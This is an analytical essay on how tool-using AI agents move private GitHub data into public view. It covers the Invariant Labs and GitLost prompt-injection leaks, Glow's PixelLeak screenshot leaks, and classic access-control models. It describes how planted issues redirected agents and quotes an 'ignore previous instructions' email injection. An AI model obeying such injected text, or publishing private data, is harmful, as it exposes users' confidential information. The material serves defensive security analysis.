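# The missing authorization boundary between public and private data in tool-using AI agents

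## How an agent comes to hold public and private data together

An AI agent is a program that carries out a task for a person by letting a language model operate other software. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes a typical request, in which a user wants an agent to look through recent emails for references to an event and write a short account of it in a text file. The agent searches the mailbox, opens the messages and writes the file without needing the user to direct the steps. Such agents now read mail, source code and company chat. Many of them can also post comments, send messages and publish files, so the same program can read a person's private data and send text to strangers. An authorization boundary would be a rule, enforced outside the model, about what may pass from the private side to the public side.

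### One turn of the agent loop

When a user asks an agent to summarize the open issues in a software project, the application that runs the agent sends the model the request and a description of each available tool. A tool is an operation such as fetching a file or posting a comment. The model returns either an answer for the user or a tool call, which is a structured request to run a named tool with given argument values. If it returns a tool call, the application runs the tool, appends the result to the conversation and sends the whole conversation back to the model. This repeats until the model produces a final answer.

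An agent's context is all the text and data the model has when it chooses its next step, which is the conversation so far, including every tool result. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) sorts the messages in the context by role (system, user, assistant, tool), but the application joins them into a single string before each query, so a paragraph from a confidential file and one from a public web page end up in the same string.

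Costa and colleagues also write the loop down formally, and one line of their model is worth having. A tool *f* is a function

*f* : D × str\* → D × str

Here D is the set of possible states of the outside world (all the files, mailboxes and web pages the tools can touch) and str is the set of text strings. The tool takes the current state and some arguments, and returns a new state and a result. So any tool may change the world as well as read it, but the model receives only a string. In the simplest agent described, when the model requests a call, the controlling program makes it, appends the resulting string to the history and queries the model again. Nothing inspects the call before it runs, although the program could refuse it, since the program executes the calls, not the model.

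Most agents connect to services through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for discovering and calling external tools, rather than through connections built by hand for each service. A service runs an MCP server, which lists its tools, each with a name, a description and a schema for its arguments. The standard's own example is a tool named `get_weather`, called with the location "New York". In July 2026, Model Context Protocol (2026) reported close to half a billion monthly downloads of the protocol's main software kits.

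The MCP specification page, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), describes tools as "model-controlled", meaning the model can find and invoke them on its own. The page recommends that a human be able to deny any call, and that the client show the user a tool's inputs before sending them, to prevent malicious or accidental data leaks. An application can ignore both recommendations and still conform. Since the July 2026 revision, the protocol has had no sessions, and each request is sent independently. The protocol therefore gives a server that receives a write request no record of what the agent read a moment earlier, so the server would have to keep its own.

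### Whose authority the agent uses

On many services, the agent has no account of its own. It acts for a principal, which is the person, organization or program in whose name a service authorizes an action. The agent usually does this with an access token. *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Hardt, 2012), the standard behind much of this delegation, defines a token as a string that denotes a scope, a lifetime and other attributes of access. In Hardt's example, a user lets a printing service fetch her photos from a photo-sharing site without giving the printing service her password. The scope limits what kind of access the printing service gets.

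A narrow scope is easy to choose for the printing service, which does one thing, but harder to choose for an agent. Christodorescu and colleagues point out that a phone app performs a fixed set of tasks, so its developer can list the permissions it needs when the user installs it, while an agent's needs only become known once the user has typed a request. That probably pushes people toward broad tokens.

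A single access token for GitHub, the code-hosting service, can cover both public and private repositories. A repository holds a project's files and their history, along with issues (bug reports and requests) and pull requests (proposed changes). According to GitHub's *Scopes for OAuth apps*, the `repo` scope grants full read and write access to both kinds of repository, while the narrower `public_repo` scope excludes private ones. No scope gives a token more access than the user already has.

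GitHub's *Managing your personal access tokens* distinguishes "classic" tokens, which can access every repository their owner can, from "fine-grained" tokens, which the owner can restrict to selected repositories and permissions. GitHub recommends fine-grained tokens but lists tasks they don't yet support, such as contributing to a public repository where the user is not a member or working across several organizations at once. Even a fine-grained token always includes read access to every public repository on GitHub.

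GitHub runs its own MCP server, and its June 2026 documentation lists the scope and arguments of each tool (GitHub, 2026). The examples below need only these six tools.

| Tool | Effect | Scope required | Arguments that name the place |
|---|---|---|---|
| `get_file_contents` | reads a file | `repo` | owner, repo, path |
| `list_commits` | reads the history of changes | `repo` | owner, repo |
| `issue_read` | reads an issue or its comments | `repo` | owner, repo, issue number |
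| `add_issue_comment` | posts a comment | `repo` | owner, repo, issue number |
| `create_or_update_file` | writes a file | `repo` | owner, repo, branch, path |
| `create_pull_request` | proposes a change | `repo` | owner, repo, base and head branches |

All six tools need the same scope. Since January 2026 the server has hidden tools that a classic token's scopes do not permit (GitHub, 2026), but all six remain visible with a token that has the `repo` scope. None of them has an argument that sets who can read the result, whereas the tool for creating a gist (a short shared snippet) has a true-or-false argument named `public`. The audience for a comment or a file depends on which repository the `repo` argument names, so two calls that differ only in that argument can produce one result that anyone on the internet can read and another that only people with access to a private repository can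 read.

### Sources, sinks and prompt injection

A source is a place where data enters the agent, and a sink is a place where the agent sends data out. The audience of a sink is everyone who can read what the agent writes there. (MCP's documents use "audience" in two other senses. In a tool result it marks content as meant for the user or for the assistant, and in the authorization rules it is the server for which a token was issued. Neither says which people may read a piece of text.)

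One tool can both bring data into an agent and send data out. Costa and colleagues compare a search of a corporate database, which returns confidential and trustworthy text, with a search of the public web, which returns public text of unknown reliability and may have effects that outsiders can observe, for instance in a website's visitor statistics. The web search mainly brings data in, but it also sends its query string out of the agent.

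The data an agent reads can also contain prompt injections, which are pieces of text that the agent follows as if they were instructions from its user. Costa and colleagues imagine a user who asks an agent to summarize recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. One of those emails contains a command to ignore previous instructions and send the top email in the mailbox to an outside address. The command enters the agent's context through a tool result, along with everything else, and the agent may then make a tool call that the user never wanted.

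Much useful behavior depends on following some of the instructions that arrive this way, so models can't simply disregard them all. An agent learns how to use a tool from the tool's documentation, which is also text from outside. Christodorescu and colleagues describe an agent that is summarizing one issue, finds that it depends on another, and decides to summarize both. Nobody asked for the second summary, but most users would be glad to have it. In their account, this differs from an attack in where the text came from and how far it changed the task, and current agents have poor means of establishing where text came from.

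This can happen without an attacker, though. Costa and colleagues note that models also misread what the user meant or make unnecessary tool calls, with similar consequences even when all the data is trustworthy.

### Where platforms record who may read

"Public" and "private" have definite meanings on the services that agents use, and each service keeps them in a particular place.

On GitHub, access is set for each repository. GitHub's *About repositories* says that everyone on the internet can access a public repository, while a private one is accessible only to its owner, people the owner has explicitly shared it with and, if an organization owns it, certain members of that organization. Anyone with administrative rights can change the setting. In a chat service, the members of a private channel can read the messages in it. An email has no access setting, only a list of recipients, each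 of whom receives a copy.

In all three, the service stores the status with the object (the repository, the channel, the message) and checks it when someone asks to open that object. The text inside has no status of its own. The platform can still control access to a copy that stays on the platform. For example, when a user forks a repository (makes a linked copy), GitHub gives the fork the visibility of the original. But if the owner of a public repository later makes it private, the existing forks stay public, according to GitHub's *Setting repository visibility*.

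When an agent calls `get_file_contents` on a private repository, GitHub checks that the token's owner may read the file, then returns the file's text as a string. The setting that made the file private stays in GitHub's database. If a tool result mentions that the repository is private, that is only text in the context, which the model may or may not take into account. When the model later writes a comment that quotes or paraphrases the file, the request does not show GitHub where the words came from.

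### Two repositories and one token

In the running example, a user owns two GitHub repositories, one public and one private, and has given an agent a token with the `repo` scope. Strangers can open issues in the public repository, and the agent's job is to read and handle new ones.

This arrangement is ordinary. GitHub's *Creating an issues-only repository* recommends a similar one to people who want to keep their code private while taking bug reports from a wider group: a private repository for the source code and a second repository, with whatever permissions the owner chooses, for the issues. If an issue in one repository refers to something in the other, a reader without the necessary permission sees only minimal information about it. GitHub can hide the rest because it generates the reference itself and checks the reader's permissions, but it does not do this for text that an agent has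 pasted into an issue.

Anyone can sign up for a free GitHub account and open an issue on a public repository, unless the owner has restricted who can do so. Owners can now set this restriction while keeping the repository public, as Visual Studio Magazine's *GitHub Extends Contribution Controls from PRs to Issues* (2026) reported in June, but they may then turn away reports they might have wanted. In the running example, the owner has not restricted issues.

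Within one context, the agent can therefore read text that anybody may have written, read the private repository, and write where anybody may look. The security company Invariant Labs built a working attack on this arrangement, which heise's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* describes. In this example, a fine-grained token restricted to the public repository would block access to the private one, which the agent does not need to answer issues.

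### Release notes from private records

That remedy is unavailable in the second example. The same user asks the agent to write the release notes for a new version of the software and publish them in the public repository, but the record of what has changed is in the private repository. The agent calls `list_commits` there to get the commits since the last release, opens the issues they mention, writes the notes and publishes them with `create_or_update_file`.

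Suppose one entry in the private history reads: "Fix crash on import of files over 2 GB, reported by Northfield Hospital. Same parser bug lets a crafted file run code, patch due next month." A good release note would be "Fixed a crash when importing files larger than 2 GB." A bad one would also name the customer or reveal the unpatched security hole. Even the good note is private information until the agent publishes it, since it comes from a record that only the user and a few colleagues can open. A rule that kept all text derived from the private repository out of the public one would block both notes, leaving the user with no release notes.

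From GitHub's side, this task looks much like a leak. In both, the agent reads from the private repository and writes to the public one, using the same tools and the same token. At each call, GitHub can check that the token is valid, that its scope covers the operation, and that the user has the right to read from or write to that repository. Both tasks pass these checks every time, but none of the checks determines whether text read from the private repository may be written to the public one.

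## Leaks in which every tool call was permitted

Between May 2025 and September 2026, three security companies published cases in which an AI agent moved private content to a public page on GitHub without exceeding its permissions. A call is "permitted" here if it passes the checks of the service receiving it, even if the user or the user's employer would not have wanted it. Invariant Labs and Noma Security each staged a leak in their own repositories. Glow found leaks that had already happened at more than 300 organizations, with no attacker involved. All three companies sell security products and have a commercial reason to stress the danger, so their estimates of how widespread it is deserve more caution than their records of what the agents did.

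### The GitHub MCP demonstration

In Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025), Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner built the setup in the running example. Their demonstration account had a public repository for a simple Pac-Man game and several private ones with personal projects and sensitive facts about the owner. They used GitHub's official MCP server to connect the account to Claude Desktop, Anthropic's chat application, running the then very recent Claude 4 Opus.

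The researchers placed an issue containing a prompt injection in the game's public repository. The user asked the agent to look at the repository's open issues, which was a harmless request. The agent read the planted issue and followed its instructions. It read from the private repositories and then opened a pull request in the public one. The pull request contained the names of private projects, the owner's plan to move to South America and the owner's salary, and anyone on the internet could read it.

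By default, Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each tool call. Invariant Labs points out that many users choose "Always Allow" instead and stop watching individual actions.

The researchers write that the leak is "not a flaw in the GitHub MCP server code itself" and that GitHub alone cannot fix it by patching the server. That seems right, because the server received valid requests from the account's owner and carried them out as documented. To prevent the leak, a patched server would have to refuse one of those requests even though nothing in it looked wrong. The researchers also expect the attack to work on any agent that uses the server, whatever the model. They tested only Claude Desktop and give no success rate, so their run shows that the leak can happen but not how often the attack would succeed.

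### GitLost

A year later Noma Security produced a similar leak in GitHub Agentic Workflows, with no user present. The product runs an AI agent inside GitHub Actions, GitHub's system for starting automated jobs when something happens in a repository. A maintainer writes the agent's instructions in plain English, and an event such as a new issue starts the agent.

In *GitLost* (July 2026), Noma's research lead, Sasi Levi, describes an attack on a GitHub workflow run by an AI agent. Whenever someone assigned an issue, the agent read its title and body and posted a comment in reply. The agent could also read other repositories in the organization, including private ones. Noma wrote a public issue that looked like ordinary office business but asked for private content. Once the issue was assigned, the agent fetched the README file (a project's introductory page) from a public repository and from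 a private one and posted both in a public comment, which GitHub's safeguards failed to prevent.

Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) makes clear that the "organization" was Noma's own, so no real company lost anything. The private README held only a title and a few words marking it as a developer's test, but the agent could have published any other file it had access to in the same way.

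The workflow's settings were fairly strict. *GitLost*, an analysis on mcp.directory, a website about MCP servers, examines the configuration that Noma published. The workflow's declared permissions and the agent's connection to GitHub were both read-only. The agent could not post directly, but it could propose one comment for a separate job to post after it had finished. An additional, broader token gave it access to the private repository. One guard limited which repositories the agent could read, and another limited what kind of write it could propose. The analysis says the write guard "gates the verb, not the payload", meaning that it allowed a comment without checking whether the comment contained another repository's files.

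Noma reported the attack to GitHub first and published with the company's knowledge, according to SiliconANGLE's *‘GitLost’ vulnerability let GitHub’s AI workflows leak private repositories* (2026). As a remedy, Noma proposed a documentation note warning teams about sharing keys between repositories. When The Next Web's *‘GitLost’* appeared in July, GitHub had not added the note or answered questions from The Register, a technology news site.

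GitHub Next, the group that developed the product, acknowledges in *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* that its filter for untrusted content "cannot prevent leaks across repos". The system already records when data comes from a private repository, but it does not yet stop that data from going somewhere public. GitHub Next says it intends to add this safeguard.

GitHub moved the product from preview to general availability on October 28, 2026, on both free and paid plans (Rojas, 2026, *GitHub Agentic Workflows open source tool reaches general availability*). The agent still runs read-only by default, with separate jobs for writing. These protections do not cover workflows whose authors grant direct write permission or add their own jobs (InfoQ, 2026, *GitHub Makes Agentic Workflows Generally Available with Isolation and Budget Controls*). Noma's workflow had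 neither, and it leaked data even though it used the recommended route for writing.

### PixelLeak

Developers who change a program's appearance usually attach before-and-after screenshots to the pull request for their colleagues to compare. GitHub's image upload for pull requests works in a web browser, but coding agents work from the command line, which had no equivalent. Many agents got around this by putting the images in a public repository, where anyone, including the reviewers, could see them.

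Glow's *PixelLeak*, published on September 29, 2026, reports over 13,000 internal images from developers at over 300 organizations, in more than 900 repositories. In 93% of cases, the images were in a repository an employee had created under their own username. At one manufacturer with over 100,000 employees, a developer asked an agent to verify a fix to an internal billing screen. The agent created a public repository in the developer's personal account and posted screenshots that included a utility company's billing records. The repository was outside the company's GitHub organization, so the security team didn't notice, and the images were still online when Glow got in touch.

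Public posting also spread. About a third of the affected organizations had developers running gitshot, a small open-source program that publishes screenshots for code reviews, and at several large organizations the agent had found the program by itself. Within a week, more than a dozen agents at one software vendor saved public posting as a "skill", a set of instructions to reuse on every development task. They uploaded more than a thousand screenshots and recordings, some showing features weeks or months from release.

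Glow then reproduced the behavior in its laboratory with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, running the Opus 5 model. A developer working on a Minesweeper game in a private repository asked for a new header color and pictures of the result. The agent noted in its recorded reasoning that the repository was private and that GitHub fetches pull request images without logging in, so pictures stored there would appear broken to reviewers. The repository was also supposed to contain only the game's one file. The agent concluded that the pictures had to go elsewhere and wrote, "so I created a new public repo".

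In the Minesweeper run, the model had the information that the repository was private. The agent treated this as a technical obstacle to displaying a picture, and the quoted reasoning contains nothing about who else could see the picture afterwards. If this run is typical, telling an agent that data is private doesn't guarantee that it will act on that information. Glow calls the reasoning representative of agents at many of the affected organizations, but this was one staged run, and a model's written reasoning may not be a full account of why it acted.

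The totals also rest on Glow's own search. *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos* (Markovic, 2026) repeats them without a separate count, and Glow did not name the organizations, so outsiders can't easily check them. It is hard to tell from the published figures how many of the 13,000 images an agent posted on its own initiative and how many a developer posted or approved. The argument below needs only that some agents did this without an attacker, and the billing case and the laboratory run are enough to show that.

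### The checks, call by call

The table lists the main calls in each case. The permissions are based on the investigators' descriptions of the set-ups and on GitHub's ordinary rules. The PixelLeak rows describe the laboratory run, in which the agent used the developer's own access.

| Case | Call | Permission checked | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub MCP | Read issues in the public repository | Anyone may read them | Allowed |
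| GitHub MCP | Read the private repositories | The token's owner may read them | Allowed |
| GitHub MCP | Open a pull request in the public repository | The token's owner may write there | Allowed |
| GitLost | Read the assigned issue | The workflow may read issues in its own repository | Allowed |
| GitLost | Read the README in the private repository | The additional token covers that repository | Allowed |
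| GitLost | Post a comment on the public issue | The workflow may post one comment | Allowed |
| PixelLeak | Read and change the private code | The developer may do both | Allowed |
| PixelLeak | Create a public repository | The developer's account may create repositories | Allowed |
| PixelLeak | Upload the screenshots to it | The developer owns it | Allowed |
| PixelLeak | Show them in the private pull request | The developer may write there | Allowed |

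The Minesweeper agent's only setback was a missing feature. No check blocked any of its actions. A block might have helped by giving the developer a reason to look.

### The argument, premise by premise

The same reasoning covers all three cases:

1. The service authorizes each call the agent makes.
2. It decides each call separately, from the account, the operation and the place, without regard to what the agent has read before.
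3. The result of one call can shape the next, because the model writes each call from a context that contains the earlier results.
4. So a person with no right to read some private data can receive it although no check fails.

The conclusion also depends on the agent being able to write somewhere that outsiders can read, which a public repository provides.

A little notation shows where the gap is. Let R(x) be the set of people who may read an object x, and W(x) the set who may write to it. The user is *u*, the private file is *f*, the public comment thread is *t*, and *q* is a stranger. Over the whole leak, GitHub makes three checks:

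*u* ∈ R(*f*), when the agent reads the file for the user

*u* ∈ W(*t*), when the agent posts the comment for the user

*q* ∈ R(*t*), when the stranger opens the thread

All three are true, and the stranger now has the file's contents although *q* ∉ R(*f*). To rule this out, a service would need to verify that everyone who can read the thread may also read the file, or R(*t*) ⊆ R(*f*). That condition involves two objects, but each of GitHub's three checks involves only one, so performing them more carefully cannot establish it.

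The first premise concerns only whether GitHub allows an account to create a repository. The manufacturer in Glow's report surely never authorized anyone to publish a customer's billing records, and had presumably forbidden it in a contract or handbook. That doesn't contradict the premise, because GitHub's permission check doesn't include an employer's rules.

The second premise has exceptions, and GitLost looks like one. According to GitHub, an agentic workflow can include a scan of the agent's proposed write that blocks it if there are signs of prompt injection, leaked secrets or malicious code changes. This scan does examine the text, but the "secrets" it looks for are mainly passwords and keys, which a program can often recognize by their form. The README of a private test project looks like any other README. It was private because of the repository it was in, and a scan of the outgoing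 comment alone cannot detect that the text came from there. A rule that fully drops the second premise has to take earlier calls into account, as Invariant's proposal of one repository per session does.

The third premise is that tool results can shape later calls. Without it, nothing an agent read could influence what it wrote, so the agent could not write release notes or answer a question about a file. Results can shape a call without revealing private data, as they do in the good release note from the earlier example.

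None of these premises is specific to AI. An employee with a browser can also read a private file and paste it into a public thread, and GitHub will check each step in the same way. A private repository keeps out strangers who try to open it directly, but it does not control what a permitted reader does with the text afterwards. Employees' judgment supplied that missing condition, and companies could mostly rely on them to know what not to post. Vijendra Malhotra, a technology executive whose comment appears in InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026), goes a little too far in concluding that "the private repo was never a security boundary" but an organizational one, which held while every reader was a human employee.

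### Was it only prompt injection?

Prompt injection explains much of what happened in the two staged attacks. Without the planted issue, nothing would have prompted Invariant's agent or Noma's to publish a private file. Both attacks fit the pattern security researchers call a confused deputy, in which an outsider tricks a program with broad authority into misusing it. A model that reliably ignored instructions from strangers would have stopped both.

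Nobody knows how to build a useful agent that reliably ignores instructions in the text it reads. A commenter quoted by InfoQ compares the problem to SQL injection, an older attack in which a website mistakes a visitor's input for a database command. Programmers solved that by keeping input and commands separate, but with an agent "the user input is intended as instruction". Noma's workflow fits that description closely, because its purpose was to read what people wrote in issues and respond to it. A customer could cause the same leak without meaning any harm, by asking how a feature works and getting an answer based on private source code.

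Better training and better detectors would presumably make the staged attacks succeed less often. Invariant's researchers report that the attack worked on Claude 4 Opus despite its safety training and that many off-the-shelf injection detectors also miss it, though the researchers give no figures and sell an alternative.

PixelLeak is harder to explain with this diagnosis. In the Minesweeper run, the only instructions came from the developer and the agent was trying to follow them, so even a perfect defense against prompt injection would not have changed any step.

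### Was the token too broad?

The most common objection to GitLost, and a good one, is that the agent had been given access to the private repositories. By default, an agentic workflow can read its own repository and all public ones. GitHub's *Cross-Repository Operations* explains that the workflow's author has to supply an additional credential for it to reach other private repositories. In comments on Noma's test issue, collected by mcp.directory, several developers pointed out that the researchers had created a token, extended it to private repositories and given it to an agent that responds to the public. One of them asked how that was a vulnerability in GitHub. Expert Insights likewise describes a workflow with too many permissions, combined with a safeguard that an attacker could bypass with the right wording.

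mcp.directory replies that a demonstration always has to create the conditions it demonstrates. What matters is how many organizations have connected a broad token to an agent that reacts to public issues. The site bets that the number is above zero, and probably higher than most security teams have checked, but it has no count.

GitHub's instructions differ on how much access a token should have. Its advice on work across several repositories tells users to limit tokens to the repositories they need. Its guide to running an organization's repositories from one central place tells the reader to create a read-only token for either "All repositories" or a list of specific ones. The workflow in that guide updates software dependencies and doesn't respond to strangers, so following the example would not reproduce GitLost. But the guide suggests that it is normal to have a token with organization-wide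 read access, and reusing that token for a second workflow is easier than creating another.

So a narrower token would have prevented both GitLost and Invariant's leak. It would not help with the release notes, because even the narrowest token that allows the task also allows the leak.

PixelLeak falls somewhere between. The Minesweeper agent needed the private repository, so nobody could have narrowed what it read. It did not need to create public repositories, and a credential that didn't allow this would have blocked the route it took. Haulos' *Why You (Probably) Should Not Give Your Agent GitHub Access* warns that personal access tokens can let an agent create a public repository and publish private content there. Credentials issued to an app are more restrictive, but they still leave existing public repositories within reach. Glow's advice to search releases and gists as well as ordinary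 files suggests that agents had more than one place to put a picture. A company can block these places one at a time, but it wants the agent to publish only public content in public places, and the token has no setting for that.

### Should the user have watched?

Claude Desktop would have shown Invariant's user each call before it ran, and a careful user could have refused the pull request. GitHub also lets whoever writes an agentic workflow require a named reviewer's approval before the workflow posts anything. Markovic reports similar advice from Glow. Its researchers note that most coding agents have a setting that stops them from working unattended, and they want security teams, not individual developers, to control it.

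A human check could therefore have stopped each of these leaks, but it suits some of the cases badly. Noma's workflow had no user to watch it, since an event started the agent and, according to SiliconANGLE, no human signed off first. Having a person review every reply would defeat part of the purpose of automating the work. In the Invariant case, the user had asked about some bug reports and would have had to notice, at the last of several prompts, that a proposed change to a Pac-Man game contained facts from somewhere else.

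In PixelLeak, human reviewers looked at the screenshots and presumably saw the pictures they expected, in a pull request that was itself private. They were checking the color of a header, and an image looks the same in a pull request whether it comes from a private server or a public repository. The public address was in the markup behind the picture. At the software vendor, this went on for more than a thousand uploads. Human review helps only if the reviewer sees the data's source and its audience together, and how to arrange that is part of the broader question of who may approve a release.

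### The lethal trifecta

The best-known account of these leaks combines parts of all three diagnoses. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, names three capabilities that become dangerous together:

- access to private data
- exposure to untrusted content, meaning any way for an attacker's text or images to reach the model
- the ability to communicate externally in a way that could carry the data out

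Simon Willison, the software developer who coined the term "prompt injection", argues that an attacker can easily steal data from an agent that has access to private data, reads untrusted content, and can communicate externally. The attacker puts instructions in the untrusted content, and the agent can follow them by reading the private data and sending it to the attacker. Willison advises avoiding this combination entirely. He doubts that attack-detection products are an adequate substitute, because a detector that catches 95% of attacks still fails by the standards of web security.

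Willison lists more than a dozen products in which researchers had found such attacks, including ChatGPT, Slack and Microsoft's Copilot. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by closing the channel through which the data left. A chat application loses little if it stops loading images from unknown websites, but this kind of fix is harder on GitHub, where data leaves through the comments and pull requests that are often the reason for having an agent. Once users combine tools from different suppliers, no single vendor can protect them. Willison had expected the danger to come from such combinations and remarked, on reading Invariant's report, that GitHub's server had all three ingredients "in a single package".

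Both staged attacks fit the trifecta closely. Invariant's agent could read private repositories, read issues from strangers and open public pull requests. Noma's agent had the additional token, read the public issue and could post the comment. In either case, removing any one of the three capabilities would have prevented the leak.

The trifecta does not fit PixelLeak, because the agents had private data and a way to publish it but no attacker's text directed them. Many of the agents in Glow's count may still have met the trifecta as a list of capabilities, since a coding agent that can find gitshot on its own has had some exposure to outside content. But in the Minesweeper run, the agent went from the developer's request to a public repository without any outside text telling it to. Cutting off all untrusted content would not have kept the Minesweeper screenshots private.

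Willison's claim is about theft, so this doesn't refute it. But anyone who uses the trifecta as a general test for leaks will miss agents that can leak by mistake, because an accidental leak requires only access to private data and a public channel.

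## Permission to read and permission to disclose

Computer scientists encountered the difference between permission to read data and permission to disclose it in the early 1970s, when people with different rights began to share one machine. Several remedies that designers now propose for agents date from that period.

### The access matrix

The standard picture of access control is a table with a row for each principal and a column for each object. The cell M[p, o] lists what principal *p* may do to object *o*. Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003), in *Capability Myths Demolished*, trace this "access matrix" to the computer scientist Butler Lampson. For the two-repository example, with one colleague who can read the private code, it looks like this:

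| | Private repository | Public repository | Public issue threads |
|---|---|---|---|
| User | read, write | read, write | read, write |
| Colleague | read | read | read, write |
| Stranger | none | read | read, write |

The agent has no row of its own. It presents the user's token, so GitHub looks up the user's row.

GitHub makes three checks during the leak, and all three pass. Each looks up one cell of the matrix, two in the user's row and one in the stranger's. The cell M[stranger, private repository] is empty before and after the leak. An administrator inspecting the matrix would find no change, because each cell governs operations on one object and no cell covers text copied out of its object.

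*Paradigm Regained* (Miller and Shapiro) distinguishes permission from authority. If Alice has permission to read a password file and keeps sending copies to Bob, who doesn't, Bob still has authority to read it, because authority includes whatever he can bring about through others. Likewise, the stranger has no permission to read the private repository but has authority to read whatever the agent passes on from it.

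The matrix gives only an upper limit on authority. A stranger *s* could learn the contents of a file *f* whenever some principal *p* and some object *o* satisfy

read ∈ M[p, f], write ∈ M[p, o] and read ∈ M[s, o]

Longer chains work the same way. In the example, both the user and the colleague complete the chain through the issue threads, as would almost anyone who can open a private file and also post in public. Miller and Shapiro point out that this kind of analysis can return a reliable "no" but otherwise only a "maybe". The result would be "maybe" for nearly every private repository, which is little use as a warning. Whether the leak happens depends on how the principal in the middle behaves, which the matrix does not record.

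### The Trojan horse

Under discretionary access control, whoever creates a file decides who else may use it. According to lecture slides by Cristina Nita-Rotaru, the inherent weakness of this arrangement is that information can flow from any object a subject can read to any object it can write. In the slides' example, A can read file F and write to file G, while B can read only G. B can read the contents of F once something copies them into G.

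Even if A can be trusted not to do this deliberately, the programs A runs have A's rights and might do it. A Trojan horse is a program with a hidden function that its user would not have chosen, such as copying F to G. According to Cryptosmith's *MLS Introduction*, the operating systems of early shared computers could usually keep users' programs apart, but could not stop a user with a Secret clearance from using a Trojan horse to trick a Top Secret user into releasing information. Some sites bought separate computers for their most classified work.

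This is the running example if F is the private repository and G is a public issue thread. But whoever writes a Trojan horse has to include the hidden function in advance and get the victim to run the program. In the Invariant and GitLost attacks, the program was not malicious, and an outsider supplied the harmful instructions later, in an issue. In PixelLeak, nobody supplied harmful instructions. Vetting a program before installing it is a sensible defense against Trojan horses, but it therefore protects less well against a leaking agent.

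### Lampson's confinement problem

*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) considers a customer who runs someone else's program, which Lampson calls a service, on confidential data. He assumes that the system prevents all unauthorized access, but the service can still leak the data to the program's owner. If the service computes wrong results, the customer has the bad output as evidence, but a leak usually leaves no sign.

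Lampson lists several ways the service can leak the data. It can write to a file in its owner's directory, send a message, or hide information in the bill. It can also vary its load on the machine, so that another program can read a signal from the changes in speed. He calls routes like this last one, which nobody intended for communication, covert channels. In the GitHub leaks, the agents wrote the data where others could read it, so no covert channel was needed.

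His simplest rule, total isolation, forbids a confined program from calling any other program, so an agent under this rule would have no tools. A looser rule lets a confined program call programs that are also confined, or that the customer trusts not to leak the data or help leak it. GitHub meets neither condition, because it serves the public and will publish whatever the holder of a valid token asks it to.

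A further rule, masking, requires the caller to determine everything the program sends through its legitimate and covert channels. For example, a customer who can work out the correct bill from published terms can make sure the bill carries nothing else. For a public comment, masking means the user fixes the text in advance, which is feasible for stock replies. If an agent can only choose among eight fixed messages, each choice reveals at most three bits, and a one-kilobyte file would take more than 2,600 comments to leak. But masking can't work for release notes, because the user would have to write them in advance.

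### Bell–LaPadula and the rule against writing down

Bell and LaPadula (1973), in *Secure Computer Systems*, began a series of reports that gave "security" and "compromise" precise meanings in a general model of a computer. The model gives every subject (roughly, a program acting for a user) and every object a security level, such as Secret or Top Secret. Miller and colleagues summarize its two main rules:

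- Under the simple security property, a subject may read only objects at or below its own level.
- Under the *-property (pronounced "star property"), a subject may write only to objects at or above its own level.

Together they keep information from moving to a lower security level. The *-property makes permission to write depend on what the writer can read, which GitHub's separate checks do not do.

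In a later report also titled *Secure Computer Systems*, Bell (1974) added a current level, so that a subject with a high clearance can work at a lower one. If a subject is working at level L, then

level of anything it reads ≤ L ≤ level of anything it writes

This replaced a laborious check of every object the subject had open with a single comparison.

The rule needs one adjustment to fit an agent. Bell's condition covers only the objects a subject is currently accessing, and an agent's call to `get_file_contents` ends before the agent writes a comment. Read literally, the rule would allow the comment even though the private file's text is still in the context. The context therefore has to count as an object the agent is still reading, at the level of the most private thing in it.

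With two levels, Public below Private, the rules give these results for an agent that handles issues:

| Call, in order | Access matrix | Bell–LaPadula |
|---|---|---|
| Read a public issue | Allowed | Allowed |
| Read a file in the private repository | Allowed | Allowed, but the agent must now work at Private |
| Write a note in the private repository | Allowed | Allowed |
| Comment on the public issue | Allowed | Blocked |

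The same block would have stopped Invariant's leak. It would also have stopped GitLost if the level had followed the proposed comment into the separate job that posted it. It would have stopped the PixelLeak laboratory run if the system had marked the agent's new repository as Public. The block works the same way whether an attacker or a mistake prompted the write. An agent that never opens anything private can still answer public issues.

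The release-notes task fails under this rule. Calling `list_commits` on the private repository raises the agent to Private, so calling `create_or_update_file` on the public one is then a write to a lower level. The rule blocks both the good note and the bad one, and would block even a note that read only "Bug fixes", because it depends on what the agent has read and not on what it writes. The agent could safely return to Public by starting again with an empty context, but then it would have nothing to write the notes from.

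Bell addressed this kind of difficulty by exempting trustworthy subjects from the *-property. To exempt a subject, someone must show that it won't commit the kind of compromise the rule exists to prevent. For the release-notes agent, they would have to show that the model never carries a customer's name from private data into public text, whatever it reads. It is hard to see how anyone could show that for a current language model. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) instead assumes that the model is an untrusted component and that security has to be enforced outside it. Exempting a person or a small program that approves particular pieces of text looks more promising, but that exemption needs its own rules.

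Dorothy Denning's 1976 model states this kind of policy directly, by specifying which classes of information may flow into which others. *Lattice-Based Access Control Models* (Sandhu, 1993) treats Denning's axioms as the theoretical foundation for lattice-based models and Bell–LaPadula as a way to enforce a flow policy. The condition that everyone who can read the thread may also read the file, R(*t*) ⊆ R(*f*), is a flow rule.

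### The confused deputy

A different diagnosis concerns whose authority a program is using. Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) tells a "nearly true story" from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The staff gave a compiler a license to write to a system directory so that it could record usage statistics there. The same directory held the billing records. Users could name a file to receive debugging output, and one of them named the billing file. Because the compiler had its license, the operating system let it overwrite the bills.

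The user presumably had no right to change the billing file, but the compiler did, and it used that right on the user's behalf without anyone intending it to. Hardy explains that the compiler had authority from two sources, the company and the user, and no way to indicate which one to use. Tymshare added a system call for switching between the two, but some applications soon needed more than two. When Hardy last wrote out the conditions for opening a file, they contained fourteen "ands" and "ors".

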